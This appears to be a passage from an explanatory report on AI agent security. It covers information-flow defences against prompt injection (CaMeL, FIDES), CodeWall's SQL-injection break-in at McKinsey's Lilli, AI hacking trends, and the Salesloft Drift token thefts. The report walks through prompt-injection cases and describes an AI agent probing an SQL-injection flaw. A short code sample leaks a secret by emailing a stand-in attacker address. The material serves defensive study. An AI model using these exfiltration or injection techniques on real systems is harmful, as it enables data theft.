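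The "millions" in Jungco's title are people who can turn on Lockdown Mode. OpenAI doesn't appear to have published how many have done so or how often they switch it off for a single chat.

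## CaMeL and FIDES: tracking each piece of data to decide where it may go

Lockdown Mode blocks the channels ChatGPT could use to send data out, whichever document the data comes from. The lawyer can't use ChatGPT in this mode to send a contract to her client, even though the client is entitled to read it. Information-flow control can restrict each document separately, because a document's labels stay with its contents as the agent works. The agent could then send the contract to the client but not to a stranger.

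The computer scientist Dorothy Denning published the mathematics of this method in 1976, and two research teams adapted it to agents in 2025. *Defeating Prompt Injections by Design*, by Debenedetti and colleagues at Google DeepMind, describes a system called CaMeL. *Securing AI Agents with Information-Flow Control*, by Costa, Köpf and colleagues at Microsoft, describes one called FIDES.

### Labels and how they combine

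A label has a secrecy part and a trust part. In the simplest version, the secrecy part marks data as public or secret, and the trust part marks it as trusted or untrusted, depending on whether an attacker could have written any of it. A more useful secrecy part lists the people who may read the data.

Suppose a company lets its legal and procurement departments read its contracts, and lets procurement and the bidder read a new bid. The contracts are trusted, but the bid is untrusted because an outsider wrote it. A procurement officer asks her AI assistant to summarize both.

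Nobody can reliably work out which document influenced which sentence of a model's output, so the software assumes that both influenced all of it. Anyone who reads the summary must therefore be entitled to read both documents:

readers of the summary = {legal, procurement} ∩ {procurement, bidder} = {procurement}

The symbol ∩ keeps only the members that both lists share. For trust, a single untrusted source makes the whole result untrusted.

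| Data | Permitted readers | Trust |
|---|---|---|
| Contracts | Legal, procurement | Trusted |
| Bid | Procurement, bidder | Untrusted |
| Summary of both | Procurement | Untrusted |

The same rule applies at every later step, so a translation of the summary or a single figure copied from it keeps the summary's label.

### The check before each tool call

Now suppose the bid contains hidden text with an order to mail the summary to the bidder. The model falls for it and writes the tool call. Before anything runs, ordinary code compares the call's labels with the company's policy. Costa and colleagues give two basic rules:

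- **Trusted action:** the agent may take a consequential action only if no untrusted data influenced the call.
- **Permitted flow:** the agent may send data only if every recipient is among its permitted readers.

The call to email the summary to the bidder breaks both rules, because the model had read the bid when it wrote the call and the bidder isn't permitted to read the summary. The software blocks the call without having to recognise the hidden sentence as an attack, so rewording the sentence wouldn't help the bidder.

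A company can require an outgoing message to satisfy both rules or accept either one. Kolluri, Sharma and colleagues (2026), in *Optimizing Agent Planning for Security and Autonomy*, accept either. The assistant can then mail the summary to procurement even after reading the bid, because procurement is allowed to read the summary. But the system also lets the summary go to the bidder if the officer herself asks for that, because it treats her request as a deliberate exception.

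This would not have helped in Anthropic's internal exercise, where an employee ran a prompt containing the attacker's instruction, because the software would have treated that instruction as the user's own. Requiring both rules should have stopped the theft, provided the company had labelled the credentials file and checked the command that sent it, but it would also have blocked many legitimate messages.

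### CaMeL: one model plans and another reads

If the same model reads the bid and decides what to do, everything it decides after reading counts as untrusted, so it can take almost no consequential actions. CaMeL avoids this by keeping the bid away from the model that makes the decisions.

Willison (2025), in *CaMeL offers a promising new direction for mitigating prompt injection attacks*, explains the design, which extends his own "Dual LLM" proposal of 2023. A privileged model sees the user's request and no documents. It turns the request into a program in a restricted form of Python. For the procurement request, the program might look like this:

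```
contracts = find_contracts("current suppliers")
bid = get_attachment("bid.pdf")
summary = ask_quarantined_model(
    "Compare the bid with the contracts", contracts, bid)
send_email(to="procurement@company.example", body=summary)
```

A second, quarantined model reads the documents. It has no tools and can only return text or a value in a format the program specifies. An interpreter, which is conventional software, runs the program line by line, calls the tools and records which variables were derived from which others. The privileged model never sees the contents of `bid` or `summary`.

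The hidden instruction now has very little effect, because the quarantined model can't send email even if it follows the instruction, and no line of the program emails the bidder.

But separating the models is not enough. If the officer asks for the summary to go to "the project lead named in the bid", the program has the quarantined model find the address, and the hidden text can make that model return the bidder's address instead. Every step runs as planned, but the summary goes to the wrong person. Debenedetti and colleagues pointed out this weakness in Willison's earlier proposal. In their example, a user wants to send a document to Bob, whose address is in a file of meeting notes.

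CaMeL can catch this because its interpreter has recorded that the address came from an untrusted file and that only procurement may read the summary. It can then refuse the call or ask the officer to approve it. *CaMeLoT* (Nikolaou, Eckhoff and colleagues, 2026) explains that each policy is a short Python function that receives the tool call and the labels of its arguments, then returns a decision with a reason. One function allows a password change only if the new password came from a trusted source.

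Willison notes that extracting a price from a document is easier than planning a task, so a company could run a smaller quarantined model on its own computers. The provider of the privileged model would then see the officer's request but none of the documents.

The drawback is that the privileged model has to write the program before the system reads the documents. The program can branch on what they contain, but only in ways the model wrote in advance. This makes the design poorly suited to requests such as "do whatever the emails from my manager ask".

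### FIDES: a planner that works with hidden text

FIDES keeps the usual agent loop, in which a model calls a tool, sees the result and chooses the next step. It also maintains a label for the conversation so far. When a tool returns data with a more restrictive label than the conversation's, FIDES stores that data in a variable and shows the planning model only the variable's name. The version that Costa and colleagues tested hid untrusted data this way but not secret data.

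For the officer's request, the planner opens the contracts and receives their text. When it opens the bid, it receives only a name such as `#bid_0`. It calls a separate model without tools to compare `#bid_0` with the contracts. The answer goes into `#summary_0`, which carries the combined label. The planner then calls the email tool with procurement's address and `#summary_0` as the body. The software replaces `#summary_0` with the real text, checks the labels and sends the message.

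FIDES hides only data that would change the conversation's label, so the planner still receives useful trusted details. For example, it might receive an email's date but not its subject or body.

FIDES also lets the planner open a variable, which CaMeL doesn't permit. Some tasks require this because the next step depends on what the document contains. The conversation then takes on the document's label. If the planner opens the bid and tries to follow the hidden order to mail the bidder, the check refuses the call.

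As an intermediate option, FIDES also lets the planner ask the separate model a question whose answer must be "yes", "no" or a choice from a fixed list. The answer to a question such as "Does the bid mention a delivery date?" is too short to contain an instruction. FIDES can record the type of answer in the label, so a policy could accept a yes or no from an untrusted document while rejecting free text. Costa and colleagues left this option out of their benchmark tests because few of the tasks needed it.

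### What the researchers proved

Costa and colleagues prove that their label-tracking method can enforce a property called *explicit secrecy*. This property requires that if an agent carries out the same sequence of operations on two copies of a company's data that differ only in their secrets, everything an outsider can see afterwards is identical. So secret text can't be copied into a public place, either directly or through a summary.

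The property doesn't cover what an outsider learns from the agent's choice of operations. If the agent calls one tool when a contract is about to expire and another when it isn't, someone who can observe the calls may work out whether the contract is about to expire. The proof also doesn't cover timing or the size of network messages.

A stronger property, *noninterference*, would also cover the agent's choices. Costa and colleagues consider it too restrictive. Under it, once the assistant had opened a contract, it could no longer use any tool whose effects an outsider might see, even to look up an exchange rate.

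The guarantee also assumes that the labels and policies are right and that the user's messages, the model and the tool descriptions are trustworthy. The proof assumes the model is deterministic, meaning the same input always gives the same output. Kolluri and colleagues make the same assumptions about trust and list malicious tool descriptions among the attacks they don't cover. PromptArmor's malicious skill for Copilot Cowork would be a similar problem if the software treated an uploaded skill as part of the user's instructions.

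CaMeL has no comparable proof. Garby, Gordon and Sands (2026), in *The LLMbda Calculus*, show how a program could get a secret past its interpreter. Their example, which adapts one from the 1970s, works roughly like this:

```
rich = True
tmp = True
if balance > threshold:
    tmp = False
if tmp:
    rich = False
if rich:
    send_email("attacker@example.com", "rich")
```

If the balance is above the threshold, the program changes `tmp`, and CaMeL marks `tmp` as secret. The line that would change `rich` then doesn't run. CaMeL marks only the variables that a program actually changes, so it never marks `rich`, even though `rich` stayed unchanged because of the balance. The email goes out, and the attacker learns that the balance is high. If the balance is low, he gets no email.

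An attacker can't normally write CaMeL's program, so he would need the privileged model to produce something like this by accident or because he had corrupted it some other way. Garby and colleagues found another gap outside the interpreter, in a loop that retries after a failure. Whether a policy blocks an attempt can depend on a secret, so each attempt can leak one bit. Because the labels don't cover the loop, they don't stop these bits from adding up. Leaking a nine-digit account number would take about 30 attempts.

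*Operationalizing CaMeL* (2025) attributes part of the difficulty to Python. For example, an error can make a Python program jump to other code in the middle of a line, which makes it hard to predict where data will go. Debenedetti and colleagues chose Python because models write it well.

### Attacks stopped and tasks completed

Both teams used AgentDojo, a benchmark with simulated office, travel, banking and Slack accounts. It has 97 ordinary tasks and a set of planted instructions meant to divert the agent. Costa and colleagues paired each task with every planted instruction from the same setting. They used an attack in which the attacker knows the agent's tools, and averaged the results over five runs.

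The table gives their results with OpenAI's GPT-4o. The completion rates are for runs without attacks and give the four settings equal weight.

| Agent | Policy checks | Tasks completed | Successful attacks |
|---|---|---|---|
| Ordinary | Off | 84.3% | 152 |
| Ordinary | On | 41.9% | 0 |
| FIDES | Off | 60.6% | 21 |
| FIDES | On | 50.0% | 0 |

The checks stopped the attacks, with or without FIDES. Hiding text in variables let the agent complete some tasks that the checks would otherwise have blocked, but FIDES still completed far fewer tasks than the unprotected agent.

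The zeros for FIDES with checks on leave out three attacks that AgentDojo's own scoring counted as successful. The researchers removed them after reading the logs. Across all the agents, they discounted cases in which the software had blocked the call, the policy allowed the action, or the attack only altered some text. They had also labelled a field as untrusted whenever one of the benchmark's attacks used it. A company can't do that, because it doesn't know where the next attack will appear. The test therefore shows that the checks work when the labels are right, but not how often people would get the labels wrong.

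Some of the loss is unavoidable under these policies. In over 40% of the banking and Slack tasks, the next step depends on what a document contains, compared with 5% of the office tasks and 10% of the travel tasks. For example, a user might ask the agent to follow payment instructions in a file. Reading the file makes the conversation untrusted, so the software blocks the payment.

Other tasks failed because GPT-4o mixed up variables or opened them needlessly. With the checks on, FIDES completed 41% of the travel tasks using GPT-4o and 68% using OpenAI's o1, a model trained to reason before it answers. Both models date from 2024, so current ones would probably fail fewer tasks. *Can CaMeLs Talk?* (2026) predicts the same for CaMeL as models improve at planning and writing code.

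*Open Challenges in Multi-Agent Security* (2025) reports that CaMeL stopped nearly all attacks in its original tests, with comparable task performance. Later tests by other researchers support the security claim but found a much larger drop in task performance. In *SecureClaw* (2026), an adapted version of CaMeL stopped all 629 attacks but completed only 29 of the 97 tasks when there was no attack. SecureClaw, a competing defence, completed 59 but let a few attacks through.

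When Nikolaou and colleagues ran CaMeL with Anthropic's Claude Haiku 4.5 and no attacks, it completed 49 of the 97 tasks. In 22 others the program didn't do what the user wanted, and CaMeL's policies blocked most of the rest. Garby and colleagues found that the policies halved CaMeL's completion rate in the banking tasks. These tests used different models and adaptations, so no single completion rate describes CaMeL, but the policies clearly account for much of the drop in completed tasks.

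### Running costs

CaMeL also uses more computing. *Indirect Prompt Injections* (2025) measured its token use on AgentDojo with GPT-4o. For the median task, CaMeL needed 2.82 times as many input tokens and 2.73 times as many output tokens as an unprotected agent. It used more tokens than any other defence in that comparison.

The cost per task can still be small. *CaMeLs Can Use Computers Too* (2026) applied CaMeL to agents that operate a computer. Running 17 tasks, with up to five tries each, cost $5.40, or about 32 cents a task. Most of that paid for the planning model, which had to write long programs covering every screen the agent might see. Adding a check on the structure of web pages raised the total to $11.57. FIDES used far more tokens than CaMeL in that setting.

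Costa and colleagues give no figures for the overhead of FIDES. They say they haven't optimised it and that each question to the separate model adds a turn.

### Counting the approvals

Kolluri and colleagues, several of whom also worked on FIDES, argue that completion rates make these defences look worse than they are. The unprotected agent in such comparisons can do anything without asking the user, while real agents often need approval for some actions. For example, GitHub Copilot's chat in Microsoft's Visual Studio Code runs read-only tools without asking but requests the user's approval before using others.

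They therefore counted the tasks that each agent could finish without any human approval. Their ordinary agent needed approval for every consequential action, while the others needed it only when a call failed the policy check. They also tested a new design called Prudentia, which is built on FIDES and tells the planner about the labels and policies so that it can avoid breaking them. With OpenAI's o3-mini, the results were:

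| Agent | Tasks finished without approval |
|---|---|
| Ordinary | 24.3% |
| Ordinary, with labels and checks | 35.5% |
| FIDES | 50.1% |
| Prudentia | 59.1% |

On this measure FIDES is well ahead of the ordinary agent. It also needed fewer total approvals for the tasks it completed, an average of 18.8 compared with 48.2. This is an advantage because users of Claude Code quickly stopped paying attention to approval requests. But the comparison assumes that a person reads each remaining request and stops any attack. FIDES would have a smaller advantage over an agent whose owner had switched approvals off.

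Prudentia can also ask the user to endorse a document instead of approving each action. If an email lists ten jobs, one endorsement replaces ten approvals. But a user who overlooks a malicious line endorses it too. Kolluri and colleagues offer no similar shortcut for secrecy, because whether somebody may share a secret usually depends on the situation.

### Policies, exceptions and labels that spread

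Somebody has to write the policies. For AgentDojo's four simulated settings, Nikolaou and colleagues count 28 CaMeL policies for tools that change something and another 46 tools whose output needs labels. A large company would need many more and have to update them whenever a tool changed.

Many labels could come from existing permissions, but they would repeat any mistakes in those permissions, such as a finance folder that the whole company can open. Costa and colleagues infer an email's readers from its sender and recipients, and acknowledge that people may have shared it more widely.

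Correct labels can also block ordinary requests. Suppose the officer wants the legal department to review the summary. Legal may read the contracts but not the bid, so the software refuses to send it. The company needs some way to allow this, such as adding legal to the bid's readers or letting the officer approve that one message.

Each document added to a piece of work can shorten the list of permitted readers but never lengthen it. After enough documents, the officer may be the only person left on the list. Researchers call the general problem over-tainting. *The Attack and Defense Landscape of Agentic AI* (2026) says that principled ways to relax labels are still needed.

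Exceptions are hard to check afterwards. Garby and colleagues point out that if a policy lets short answers through, a reviewer can't tell whether a particular "yes" was harmless or part of a leak. Even if an exception is safe once, it may need a limit on how often the agent can use it, because a series of short answers can reveal a whole secret.

Debenedetti and colleagues write that prompt injection is "not fully solved". As limitations, they note that policies take work to maintain and that users can tire of approving exceptions. Willison is enthusiastic about CaMeL but nervous about any design that requires users to think about security policies. He has worked in application security for two decades and says he still hasn't fully figured out Amazon's permission system. He hopes for well-chosen defaults and a clear interface.

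### False summaries and unchecked exits

Labels control where a summary goes, but hidden text can still make the summary false, as with Lockdown Mode. The label would at least mark the summary as untrusted, which gives the officer a reason to read the bid herself. A stricter policy could bar the assistant from sending any text derived from an untrusted document, but then it could never send her a summary of a bid.

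The checks also have to cover every way data can leave. Costa and colleagues check only tool calls because they assume that showing an answer to the user is harmless, though they note that a developer can check answers too. A product that displays external images would need to check answers or block the images to stop an attack like EchoLeak.

Copilot Cowork's message to its own user is a harder case. The user is allowed to read her own files, so the permitted-flow rule allows the message even though its images leak her download links. To catch this, the policy would have to count the owner of every image server as a recipient. Claude Cowork's upload to Anthropic raises the same issue, because who can read the file depends on whose account receives it.

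### Successors and products

Several projects from 2026 try to fill these gaps. Before CaMeL's program runs, Nikolaou and colleagues' CaMeLoT translates it into a diagram of possible steps and uses a model checker, a tool that searches such diagrams for any path that breaks a rule. If the checker finds one, the privileged model gets a description of it and tries to repair the program.

This allows rules about the order of events, such as "obtain approval before disconnecting a computer from the network", which CaMeL can't easily express because it checks one call at a time. In a test, CaMeLoT caught all seven unsafe programs and a simplified CaMeL caught one, although the researchers chose the rules to be beyond CaMeL's reach. CaMeLoT can't check everything in advance. For example, who may read a file is often known only when the agent opens it, so CaMeL still has to check permission as the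 program runs.

Garby and colleagues designed a small programming language, LLMbda, in which every value carries a label. They proved a form of noninterference for every program in it, including programs that a model writes as it goes, and checked the proof by computer. A program can still leak information through whether it finishes. Their agent completed about as many banking tasks as CaMeL did without its policies, and resisted all but 2 of 1,296 attacks. The proof doesn't rule out such failures because it covers how the language handles labels, not whether a company's policy forbids every harmful action.

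*Can CaMeLs Talk?* extends CaMeL to several cooperating agents, so that text planted in one agent's data can't redirect another. *From Agent Traces to Trust* (2026) describes two projects that track influence in finer detail. NeuroTaint traces influence through the model and the conventional software around it, and Agent-Sentry checks whether untrusted sources affected the sensitive arguments of a tool call.

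Microsoft's *Stop prompt injection from hijacking your agent* (2026) announced on 20 May that developers could use FIDES in Agent Framework, the company's toolkit for building agents. Microsoft's documentation lists three kinds of secrecy label: public, private and tied to a user's identity. The procurement company would need labels tied to identities, because if it marked both the contracts and the bid simply as private, the software could not tell procurement from the bidder.

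## McKinsey's Lilli: an AI agent breaks into a store of company documents

CaMeL and FIDES control what an assistant does with the documents it reads, but they don't help if an intruder takes the documents straight from the database behind the assistant. On 28 February 2026, an AI agent broke into such a database without using prompt injection. The database was behind Lilli, the assistant that the consulting firm McKinsey built for its more than 43,000 employees. The agent belonged to CodeWall, a start-up that tests companies' security. CodeWall reported the flaws to McKinsey and published its account on 9 March.

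McKinsey consultants use Lilli to search the firm's research, analyse documents and plan client work. The firm launched it in 2023, and it handles more than 500,000 prompts a month. In early 2025 Jacky Wright, then McKinsey's technology chief, told the technology news site The Stack that the firm had put all of its knowledge into Lilli's search index.

### How the agent got in

CodeWall's *How We Hacked McKinsey's AI Platform* says the agent started with a domain name and no password. The agent found public documentation for more than 200 of Lilli's endpoints, the addresses where other software sends requests. Most required a login, but 22 didn't, and one of those saved users' search queries in the database.

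That endpoint was open to SQL injection. Its requests were in JSON, a common format that pairs each value with a field name, as in `"supplier": "Acme"`. Lilli's programmers had used parameterised queries to keep values, such as Acme, out of the database command, but the software pasted field names, such as supplier, straight into it. A consultant using the search page can't change the field names, because the page fills them in. But anyone who sends requests directly to the endpoint can choose any field names, including ones that contain SQL.

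The placeholders in parameterised queries protect values but not the names of tables and columns, according to guidance from the software-security organisation OWASP that D'Angelo cites in *McKinsey's Lilli Looks More Like an API Security Failure*. A database has to know which column a command refers to before it can prepare the command. Programmers can instead check each name against a fixed list and reject any that isn't on it.

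The database's error messages repeated the field names it had received, which showed the agent that the text it sent was reaching the command. Over fifteen attempts, the agent used the errors to work out the command's structure, until it got back real employee data. It also found that Lilli's software returned some records without checking whether the user was allowed to see them, and it used this flaw to read individual employees' search histories.

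Paul Price, CodeWall's founder, told The Stack that the break-in took two hours and $20 worth of model use. He said McKinsey's own tools and outside testers had missed the flaw for more than two years. CodeWall also tried a widely used scanner, which failed to detect the flaw, probably because most such tools test values but not field names.

CodeWall says that no human guided the agent and that the agent itself suggested McKinsey as a target. Price described a larger human role to The Stack, saying he had asked a model to find prominent organisations with public policies on reporting security flaws. He chose what kind of target to look for and decided to attack.

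### What the agent could reach

CodeWall gives these figures for what it could reach:

| Contents | Number |
|---|---|
| Chat messages, stored unencrypted | 46.5 million |
| Files | 728,000 |
| User accounts | 57,000 |
| Passages from reference documents | 3.68 million |
| Model configurations, including system prompts | 95 |

The second row is disputed. The Financial Times' *McKinsey rushes to fix AI system after hacker exposes flaws* describes it as a list of file names and quotes a person close to McKinsey who said the files themselves were stored separately and "never at risk". CodeWall says the database also contained download addresses but doesn't say that the agent opened any.

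Storing the original files separately would have protected them, but a search system also keeps copies of passages from the documents it searches. An intruder who could read 3.68 million of those passages would often not need the originals. CodeWall describes the passages as McKinsey's own research, so they may have contained little from clients.

McKinsey says in its *Statement on strengthening safeguards within the Lilli tool* (2026) that it fixed the flaw within hours. It also says an investigation with an outside forensics firm found no evidence that the researcher or any other unauthorised person had accessed client data. The statement gives no figures and doesn't mention staff data or the firm's own research.

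Both accounts can be true. Kiledjian (2026), in *CodeWall says it hacked McKinsey's AI platform. Here's what holds up*, objects that CodeWall blurs the difference between data its agent could have reached, data it read and data it copied. A short query can return the number of rows in a table, so the agent could have counted 46.5 million messages without reading any. Copying them all within two hours would have required taking about 6,500 a second, and CodeWall doesn't claim to have done that. The search histories are harder to reconcile with McKinsey's statement. CodeWall says they revealed what people were working on, which at a consulting firm is usually work for a client.

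Kiledjian thinks the flaw is credible but the claimed scale is unproven, because CodeWall published no screenshots or copies of the agent's requests. Price says McKinsey's staff read and amended the post before publication, which lends the post some support, but McKinsey hasn't publicly confirmed the numbers.

McKinsey's finding of "no evidence" may not rule out an earlier theft. If the flaw was open for two years, investigators would need detailed logs for that whole period, and McKinsey hasn't said how far back its logs go. Kiledjian also thinks the nine days between discovery and publication left little time for a thorough check.

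CodeWall had a commercial reason to make the break-in sound as serious as possible. Price was its only employee in March, and his post ends with an invitation to prospective customers. SC Media UK's *CodeWall launches with $4 million to offer autonomous AI hacking agents* cites the McKinsey break-in as a demonstration of the product CodeWall launched in October.

There is also some doubt about whether CodeWall had permission. Price told The Stack that he considered McKinsey's disclosure policy explicit authorisation. Kiledjian replies that nobody has confirmed that the policy covered Lilli's live database.

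### Why it matters who can rewrite the prompts

According to CodeWall, the agent could change the database as well as read it, and the database contained Lilli's system prompts. An attacker could have rewritten them with one command, for example to add an instruction to include confidential figures in answers. Consultants could then have pasted those figures into documents for other clients.

An attacker who can rewrite the system prompt can replace the developer's instructions instead of trying to override them with text planted in an email. Training a model to distrust outside text gives no protection against this, because the model can't distinguish the altered prompt from the original. Neither can a consultant who sees only the answers.

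CodeWall doesn't report changing a prompt. It says that such a change "leaves no log trail", but Kiledjian considers this too absolute because some companies log every database change or keep old versions of their settings.

A company can make tampering much easier to notice by storing a short digital fingerprint of each approved prompt where the database account can't alter it, and having the software check the prompt against its fingerprint before each use. Wharton's *Two Early 2026 AI Exposures* (2026) recommends integrity checks of this kind and a version history that lets staff undo unauthorised changes. It also advises companies to ask after any break-in whether somebody altered the model's behaviour, and whether they need to recheck the answers it gave in the meantime.

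### An old flaw and a new kind of store

D'Angelo, whose company sells security tools for AI systems, describes the case as an ordinary software failure that reached an AI system. SQL injection is decades old, and leaving an endpoint without a login is an even simpler mistake. In his view, the AI mattered because it increased the harm a breach could do.

Lilli's database covered the whole firm, whereas an intruder in one project team's folder gets only that team's documents. It also held the questions consultants had asked while still working out what to advise, a kind of record that hardly existed before.

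Companies with much simpler systems also accumulate conversations. Wharton compares Lilli with the repair company Sears Home Services, where the researcher Jeremiah Fowler found three databases with no password. They held 3.7 million transcripts of customers' chats with AI assistants and 1.4 million audio recordings, some of which ran for hours and picked up household noise after the call ended. Fowler didn't need a hacking agent to find them, and most of the harm came from the company's decision to keep them.

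CodeWall then attacked McKinsey's two main rivals. CodeWall's *How We Hacked BCG's Data Warehouse* describes an endpoint at Boston Consulting Group that ran any database command without requiring a login. At Bain, the agent found a working username and password within 18 minutes, in a file the website sent to every visitor (CodeWall's *How We Hacked Bain's Competitive Intelligence Platform*). Both firms fixed the flaws quickly but played down the damage. According to Rankiteo's *Bain & Company and Boston Consulting Group*, BCG said the database was isolated and held anonymised, public data, and Bain disputed CodeWall's account of the scope.

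CodeWall presents this as three successes out of three. It doesn't say whether its agent tried other companies and failed, and it picked BCG and Bain because it expected them to have made the same mistakes as McKinsey. The results are good evidence that such mistakes are common among firms building similar products in a hurry, but they don't show how often the agent would succeed against companies in general.

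### Are attackers gaining from AI?

The UK's AI Security Institute (AISI), a government body that tests advanced models, measures models' hacking ability by the length of the tasks they can complete. It gives them self-contained problems, such as breaking into a website, and estimates how long each would take a human expert. Claude Sonnet 4.5 succeeded 80% of the time on tasks that take an expert about 16 minutes.

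In November 2025 AISI estimated that this length was doubling every eight months. By February 2026 it had shortened that estimate to 4.7 months, according to its *How fast is autonomous AI cyber capability advancing?*, published in May. Over a year, the length would grow about 2.8 times at the first rate and about 5.9 times at the second. Anthropic's Claude Mythos Preview and OpenAI's GPT-5.5 then exceeded both trends.

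These figures are uncertain at the top end. Only six of the tasks take an expert eight hours or more, and Mythos Preview completed all six every time, so the test can no longer measure the limit of its ability. AISI also limits how much text a model can process on each task, so the figures understate what an attacker with a larger budget could do. But some scores could be too high, because AISI reported in July that it had found models cheating in all of its hacking tests.

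AISI's larger tests use simulated company networks. One requires 32 steps and would take a human expert about 20 hours. Mythos Preview completed it in three of ten attempts in April, and a newer version did so in six of ten in May. But these networks have no staff watching for intruders, the model starts with access, and setting off an alarm carries no penalty. AISI therefore says it can't be sure that Mythos Preview could attack a well-defended system.

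When a model runs on its developer's servers, the developer can detect misuse and close the attacker's account. Developers can't do this with an open-weight model, which anyone can download and run. AISI found that recent open-weight models were four to seven months behind the best closed ones at hacking, compared with six to ten months through most of 2025. The Decoder's *Open-weight models now match frontier cyber performance from just four months ago* reports that GLM-5.2, released in June 2026, matched Claude Opus 4.6 from February. AISI warns that this doesn't show whether open-weight models will catch up as quickly with Mythos Preview and GPT-5.5.

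Criminals and spies were already using AI in 2025. That August, Anthropic reported that a criminal had used Claude Code to steal data from at least 17 organisations, including healthcare providers and emergency services, and had demanded ransoms that sometimes exceeded $500,000. In November it reported that a group it believed was sponsored by the Chinese state had used Claude in a spying campaign against about 30 organisations. Anthropic estimated that AI did 80 to 90% of the work. The group got into only a few of its targets, and Claude sometimes reported passwords that didn't work or presented public information as secret.

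Later cases suggest that attackers now need less skill. *A newbie hacker used "vague, low-skill prompts" in Claude and Codex* (Fadilpašić, 2026) describes a beginner who broke into 14 companies while AI agents did the routine work, although he left serious gaps in his own security. In December, *Autonomous AI Hacker Targets Perplexity, Reportedly Breaches Two Other Companies* (The Hacker News, 2026) reported that the AI search company Perplexity had blocked an AI agent looking for credentials to its cloud services. Related attacks obtained such credentials at two other companies.

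This evidence suggests that AI lets attackers afford to try many more targets, though it doesn't establish how many of the thefts would have happened without AI. Fortune (2026) puts the traditional price of a mock attack by human testers at about $30,000. At Price's $20 per target, the same money would pay for 1,500 attempts, and if only 1% of the targets had a flaw that the agent could find, it would get into 15 of them. This comparison overstates the agent's advantage, since human testers cover more ground and the $20 leaves out the cost of building the agent. But even at $200 per target, a company could no longer assume that it was too small or obscure to be attacked.

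### Whether defenders can find the flaws first

A company can run the same kind of agent against its own systems, and it has some advantages over an attacker. It can test before launch and give the agent the source code. The step that pasted field names into Lilli's commands would have been much easier to see in the code than from outside. AISI's engineers used advanced models this way to look for mistakes in the set-up of their own research platform.

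Companies can also run cheaper tests more often. If a company tests once a year and finds every flaw each time, a flaw introduced at a random moment stays open for six months on average. Weekly tests would reduce this to three or four days. But McKinsey's tests had missed Lilli's flaw for two years, so running the same tests more often would not have found it. Finding it required a test that tried field names, which CodeWall's agent happened to run.

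Finding a flaw before attackers do helps only if it is also repaired before they can use it. The software company Pixee (2026) describes how researchers spent about $25 on GPT-5.6 Sol Ultra to find a flaw in WordPress, the website software, that let an outsider run code without a login. WordPress released a fix on 17 July 2026, and attackers were using the flaw within 72 hours. Attackers can study a public fix to locate the flaw, and every website that hasn't installed the fix remains vulnerable. McKinsey had an easier job because it runs the only copy of Lilli and could repair it for everyone at once.

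Safety limits on AI models may also block defenders' work. In July, AI agents broke into Hugging Face, a company that hosts AI models. Safety limits on the models Hugging Face was using blocked its forensic work, so it had to switch to an open-weight model. OpenAI later reported that its agents had probably carried out the attack during a test. A developer could loosen the limits for known security teams, but it would need to check who they were, and a company can't wait long for approval during a break-in.

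### Measures that would have reduced the loss

A login requirement on all 22 endpoints would have stopped CodeWall's agent, which had no account. The safest way to do this is to have the software refuse every request without a login unless a programmer has listed the endpoint as an exception, so that a forgotten endpoint stays closed. But the SQL flaw would have remained, and a thief with the password to any of the 57,000 accounts might have been able to use it.

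McKinsey could also have restricted the database account used by the endpoint, which saved search queries. If that account had only been able to add rows to one table, injected SQL could not have read the chat messages or changed a prompt. According to CodeWall, Bain made the same mistake on a larger scale, with an account that could read and change 11 databases.

**Separate stores** extend the same idea. System prompts change rarely and only a few people need to edit them, so a company can keep them outside the main database and require a second person to approve each change. It can also store each client's documents in a separate database. If a firm divided its documents evenly among 500 clients, an intruder in one database would get 0.2% of them. The assistant would then have to search only the databases that the signed-in consultant may open, which would make questions across the whole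 firm slower or impossible to answer.

Encryption helps only if the intruder can't use the key. Many databases encrypt their disks, which protects against theft of the hardware, but they decrypt the data automatically for any query, including an injected one. A company can avoid this by encrypting each client's messages with a different key and having a separate service release a key only for a signed-in employee who works for that client. An attacker who used the Lilli flaw would then have obtained mostly unreadable text. But a database can't easily search encrypted text, so this method suits old conversations better than the search index.

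Companies also need to keep credentials out of their records. Bain's activity log contained 36,869 complete login tokens beside employees' email addresses. Each token was valid for a year, so anyone who could read the log could sign in as those employees.

**Short retention** limits how much an intruder can steal, however they get in. If Lilli collected its 46.5 million messages evenly over 30 months, deleting each message after one month would have left about 1.55 million in the database, or 97% fewer. But consultants would lose their older conversations, and some firms are legally required to keep records. Investigators also need a history after a theft, but an audit log can record who opened which document without copying the text.

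Apple introduced Private Cloud Compute in 2024 for AI requests that are too demanding for an iPhone. Its servers delete the data once they have produced an answer, so an intruder would find the requests in progress but no archive of earlier ones. Apple built the servers without the remote access that administrators normally have. It also publishes their software for researchers to inspect, and the phone sends requests only to servers it can verify are running that software.

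Lilli couldn't work entirely like this, because it needs a permanent collection of documents to search. McKinsey could still have treated conversations this way and left any history on the consultants' own laptops, though that would have made it harder for colleagues to share their work. It would also have had to deal with any copies kept by suppliers, since deleting a conversation from Lilli doesn't delete those. CodeWall says that 1.1 million files passed through outside AI services, and that it found more than 266,000 document indexes at OpenAI.

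## The Salesloft Drift thefts: stolen access tokens and what the logs showed

A supplier can expose a company's records without keeping a copy of them if its software has permission to read them. Drift, an AI chat product from the sales-software firm Salesloft, had such permission. Companies put Drift on their websites to talk to visitors and connected it to Salesforce, where they kept their customer records. In August 2025, thieves who had stolen the access tokens for these connections used them to export the records.

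*Widespread Data Theft Targets Salesforce Instances via Salesloft Drift* (Larsen, Lin and colleagues, 2025) is Google's account of the thefts, which lasted from at least 8 to 18 August. Google told The Hacker News (2025) that it knew of over 700 potential victims. Some of them may not have had any data stolen.

### How an access token works

To connect Drift to Salesforce, an administrator signs in to Salesforce and approves the permissions that Drift requests. Salesforce then gives Drift an access token, following a widely used standard called OAuth. Drift attaches the token to each request, and Salesforce checks that the token is valid and that its permissions cover the request. The administrator can cancel the token without changing her password.

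However, Salesforce doesn't check who is sending the usual kind of token, so anyone who copies one gets the same access as Drift. Access tokens often expire within hours, but the supplier also receives a refresh token, which it can exchange for new ones. A chatbot needs this to keep working at night, when nobody is there to sign in again. Someone who steals a refresh token can usually keep renewing their access until somebody revokes the token.

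### One break-in, many customers

The thieves first got into Salesloft's GitHub account. Between March and June 2025, they downloaded code, added a guest user and explored the company's systems, according to Help Net Security's *Salesloft Drift data breach*. CyberScoop quotes Salesloft as saying that the thieves then got into Drift's systems on Amazon's cloud and took customers' tokens. Salesloft did not explain how they got into the GitHub account.

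The thieves sent their queries directly to Salesforce, not through the chatbot, so training the chatbot to resist planted instructions would have made no difference. But AI products are still attractive targets for token thieves. These products are more useful when they connect to more services, so their suppliers accumulate tokens.

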